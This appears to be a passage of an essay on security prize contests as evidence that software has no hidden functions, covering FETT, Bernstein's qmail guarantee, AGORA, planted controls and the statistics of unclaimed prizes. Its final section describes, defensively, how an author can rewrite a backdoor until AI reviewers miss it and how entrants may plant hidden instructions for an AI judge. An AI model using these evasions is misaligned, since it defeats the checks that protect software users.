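DARPA provided programs with known weaknesses to run on the processors. IEEE Spectrum's *Darpa Hacks Its Secure Hardware, Fends Off Most Attacks* explains that challengers could also write any vulnerable program of their own and try to exploit it in a way that contradicted the security claims. Most of the reports came from this second approach. One challenger stole the component that checks Linux passwords from a protected area by attacking the firmware that was supposed to guard it.

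DARPA (2021) notes that challengers had only virtual access to the processors. They could not put a probe on a chip to measure its power consumption, so the contest has little bearing on leaks that such measurements could reveal.

DARPA considered the result a success, and ten holes in 13,000 hours suggests that the processors were hard to attack. The published totals don't show how many holes remain, but a record of which teams found each hole might have allowed an estimate. Suppose one team finds six holes and another finds five, and three of them are the same. The second team found half of the first team's holes. If it also found half of all the holes, there are about ten in total, and the teams have missed about two. A contest that pays only the first person to report a hole loses this information, because nobody else has a reason to report it.

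### When nobody can pull the trigger

A contest that pays only for a working demonstration has a serious flaw, because a challenger can find a backdoor and still lose. If the adding service compares the hash of each pair of numbers with a stored number K, a challenger can see the suspicious branch but can't find the pair that activates it.

As a remedy, FETT's rule suggests letting challengers alter the conditions of the test. A challenger could choose his own pair, replace K with that pair's hash, and show that the altered service returns another customer's number. This would show that the author's claim depends on an unexplained number, though it wouldn't prove that anyone knows a pair for the original K. The organisers could then require the author to remove the branch or prove that nothing can activate it.

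The same demonstration would also have worked if Juniper's random number generator had been designed honestly, because anyone who chooses the constant in Dual_EC can predict its output. The sensible rule there would be to require the author to explain how they chose the constant.

### A bet on a lock

In 2024, a critic of guaranteed safe AI bet $10,000 against a supporter's $1,000 that nobody would soon build a mechanical lock with a valid proof that it can't be picked. The critic wins at the end of 2026 if there is no formally verified design, if the proof doesn't exclude mechanical picking, or if fewer than three matching copies exist. Otherwise, experts have until the end of 2027 to pick the lock, perhaps in an open challenge at DEF CON, and the supporter wins if credible attempts fail.

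The experts must have access to the design in advance, and the design must allow at least a thousand different keys. Leaving draws aside, the critic's break-even point is a one in eleven chance that the lock succeeds.

The two men did not define picking. Another participant asked whether a custom-built device would count, and suggested that a robot arm that takes the key from the owner's pocket should not. Somebody replied that finding a definition without holes is much of the difficulty of the proof, so it made little sense to demand one before the bet. The two men left disputes to an arbiter both had accepted. The wager about a false Lean proof, in *Can you hear the shape of a Lean soundness bug*, similarly depends on what experts notice.

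The most useful rule is that if nobody makes a credible attempt, the bet is a draw and each man gives half his stake to charity. Bernstein's guarantees have no such rule, so a year in which nobody examined qmail would have added to its record just as a year of intense scrutiny would.

Together, the existing schemes supply most of the rules for the contest:

| Rule | Precedent |
|---|---|
| The author offers money against his own claim | Bernstein |
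| A neutral person holds the money for a fixed term, and a committee judges | Sill |
| Challengers may attack the statement before the program | Devcon, Certora |
| Challengers may construct their own situations | FETT |
| Software measures a published list of observables | Spec Hunt |
| One underlying fault wins once | Spec Hunt |
| An unattempted challenge counts for nothing | the lock bet |

The claims in these schemes are all narrower than "it does nothing else".

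### What the prize has to compete with

A prize has to persuade people to search, and then to report what they find. Persuading them to search can require a large prize. Suppose a thorough search costs a challenger $10,000 in time, there is a 10% chance that the program has a hidden function, and a searcher finds it half the time if it exists. A lone challenger has a 5% chance of winning, so the prize must be at least $200,000 to cover his costs on average. If five people search and the prize goes to one of those who succeed, each has about a 1.9% chance of winning, and the prize must be at least about $516,000.

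At a 1% chance of a hidden function, those prizes would have to be ten times as large. The cleaner a program looks, the less anyone gains by checking it, and an unclaimed prize of ordinary size may then mean only that nobody bothered. Had qmail's fault taken as long to find as an average one in FETT, $1,000 would have paid 77 cents an hour. (Guninski evidently had other reasons to look, and reputation can be worth more than the money.)

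Anyone who finds a flaw can also sell it or use it. A way to take over accounts on a million mail servers would have been worth far more than $1,000 to a criminal. The comparison is easier for smart contracts, since the money a contract holds is often a direct measure of what a thief could take. If a contract holds $50 million, a $10,000 prize attracts mainly people who would never have stolen the money.

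An honest author with a good program can offer a large prize cheaply, because he expects to get it back. He still has to deposit the money, because a promise to pay half a million dollars is worth little from somebody who doesn't have it or who alone decides whether he owes it.

### What an unclaimed prize shows

Imagine 1,000 programs, each from an author who claims that it does nothing else, and suppose that 100 of them have a hidden function. Five challengers examine every program. Each finds a hidden function half the time, independently of the others, and reports it. All five miss it with probability

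    (1/2)^5 = 1/32

so about 3 of the 100 get through. Challengers report nothing for those 3 or for the 900 clean programs. The chance that an unchallenged program has a hidden function is therefore about 3 in 903, or 0.35%, down from 10%.

In general, if p is the probability of a hidden function before the contest and m is the probability that every challenger misses it, the probability after an unsuccessful contest is

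    p × m / (p × m + 1 − p)

All the difficulty is in m. Suppose that 30% of hidden functions are beyond every challenger, for example because they depend on a secret constant or on a machine that nobody will own for another seven years. Each of the five challengers still has a 50% chance of finding any one of the others. Then 30 of the 100 programs with hidden functions pass the contest, as do about 2 of the other 70, and the probability that a program that passes has a hidden function is 32 in 932, or 3.5%.

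| Challengers | Any hidden function can be found | 30% are beyond all challengers |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 10% | 10% |
| 1 | 5.3% | 6.7% |
| 5 | 0.35% | 3.5% |
| 10 | 0.01% | 3.2% |

Adding more challengers of the same kind can't bring the figure below 30 in 930, or about 3.2%. Making them better at finding the discoverable functions hardly helps either. If each challenger found five sevenths of the discoverable functions, which is half of all hidden functions, five challengers would still leave the figure at 3.2%.

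The share of flaws that no challenger can find is seldom known, but it isn't zero. In Jane Street's contest, which tushard describes, two of the planted backdoors were not fully identified by anyone. An author who plants a backdoor and then offers a prize presumably expects nobody to find it. Prizes may therefore attract the kind of backdoor to which the last column of the table applies. They should work better for accidental flaws, which nobody designed to escape a search.

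The calculation also assumes that challengers try hard and report honestly. If each of the five has only a one-in-five chance of searching seriously, the probability falls only from 10% to 6.2%. If all five search seriously but report only half of what they find, and sell or keep the rest, it falls to 2.6%.

### Paying people who find nothing

*AGORA* (Chen, Zhou and colleagues, 2024) describes a system that deals with the problem of effort by paying for the answer "no bug". The system checks whether a compiled program obeys a security policy, such as staying within its own memory. It turns that question into logical formulas, which anyone may try to solve by any method. A solution to any formula would mean the program might break the policy.

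A solution is easy to check, since a computer can substitute it into the formula. But a worker who reports that no solution exists might not have looked for one. AGORA therefore sends each worker a bundle that mixes genuine formulas with fabricated ones that have known solutions. It rewrites the formulas to make the two kinds hard to tell apart, and varies the number of fabricated ones so that a worker can't stop after finding the expected number of solutions. Anyone who fails to solve a fabricated formula gets nothing. Workers who solve all the fabricated formulas receive roughly the cost of the computation, and a much larger reward if they also find a real fault.

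Chen and colleagues also want to count different methods, because ten people using the same software are likely to find little more than one would. If 70% of the answers come from distinct methods, then after 21 reports of "no bug" there is a better than 99% chance that at least ten methods have examined a given function. The 70% is an assumption, and different methods can miss the same faults. The design also assumes that honest workers can find the faults, so it has no equivalent of the 30% that nobody could find. The group built only part of the bounty system, including the contract that handles payments and the check on reported solutions, and left fabricating tasks for later. No contest has yet tested whether workers could tell the fabricated formulas from the genuine ones.

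Code4rena, which organises security contests, offers a simpler way to pay for catching known faults. Its *Blockswap Formal Verification Contest with Certora* (2023) assigned 55% of the money to specifications that catch real bugs, 35% to those that catch bugs the organisers had injected, and 10% to participation. If there were no real bugs, 78% would go to catching injected bugs and 22% to participation, so entrants could still count on the full sum being paid out.

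Contests can also pay for proofs. In one for the Rust programming language's standard library, participants prove that functions are safe. According to the Rust Foundation's *How the Rust Standard Library Verification Contest Scaled Past Manual Proof Engineering*, they found no previously unknown memory-safety vulnerabilities, but they did find errors in specifications and documentation, which have since been fixed. A valid proof holds permanently for its function, regardless of the entrant's effort or honesty, so finding no vulnerabilities is much more informative here than in a search for bugs.

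### How many planted functions are enough

Planted controls, which earlier experiments used to score reviewers, can also estimate m. Suppose the organisers plant 30 hidden functions and the challengers, taken together, find them all. The best single estimate of their miss rate is zero, but a group that misses one in twenty would also find all 30 about a fifth of the time. The largest miss rate consistent with the result at 95% confidence satisfies

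    (1 − m)^30 = 0.05

which gives m = 9.5%, or about 10%. If they had missed three of the 30, the upper limit would be about 24%. Getting it down to 1% would take about 300 planted functions, all found.

With m at 9.5%, an unclaimed prize would reduce a 10% probability of a hidden function to about 1%, but only if any hidden function would be like the planted ones. If 3 of the 10 percentage points come from a kind that nobody planted and the challengers can't find, the probability falls only to about 3.9%.

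The organisers also have to hide the planted functions from challengers who know the author's program. If the original is public, anyone can find the planted functions by comparing an altered copy with it. The organisers could instead give out several unpublished programs of similar size and style, some with planted functions, and mix the author's program in with them. They should write down beforehand what they planted and publish a cryptographic commitment to it, as *A public $51.2K backdoor-recovery challenge* did with its answer, so that they can't quietly drop the functions that everyone missed.

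Such controls would also show which methods work. If the challengers found every strange branch but none of the timing leaks, the author could claim support for what he said about branches but not for what he said about timing.

### AI challengers

AI models have made searching much cheaper. kirancodes writes in *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* that the cost of discovering security bugs "is collapsing", and OpenAI's search of the Linux kernel is a good example. If a thorough search costs $100 instead of $10,000, the prize needed to make it worthwhile for a single challenger falls from $200,000 to $2,000. The organisers could also pay for the searches themselves. Testing challengers on 300 planted functions, with one search per function, would cost $30,000 instead of $3 million.

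An AI model can also work without remembering its previous attempts, so organisers can give it many programs without it learning what they tend to plant. Its false alarms matter less than in ordinary screening because a machine can reject any claim without a working demonstration. If an AI also judges the entries, entrants may try to manipulate it. Paradigm screens every Spec Hunt entry for hidden instructions before the reviewing agent reads it.

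The main drawback is that copies of the same model don't search independently. Suppose five copies each find half of all hidden functions, but always the same half. Then m is 1/2 instead of 1/32, and an unclaimed prize leaves the probability at 5.3%, as it would with a thousand copies. Real copies vary somewhat from run to run, so the true m lies between these values, and testers can estimate it using planted functions. If one run finds 15 of the 30 planted functions and ten runs together find only 17, the other nine have added very little. Models from different companies may differ more, though they learn from much of the same text.

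Before publishing a program, its author can use the contest's models to rewrite a hidden function until none of them finds it, just as an attacker can rewrite code until the compiler gives no warnings. If the models then found nothing in the contest, that would be no evidence against a deliberate backdoor, however well they had done on the planted ones. To prevent this, the organisers could make the author deposit the program first and use only models that became available afterwards. Wheeler's test for a subverted compiler similarly works best with a second compiler chosen after the attack. The organisers could search the same deposited file again with each new generation of models, for as long as the author wants to keep making the claim.
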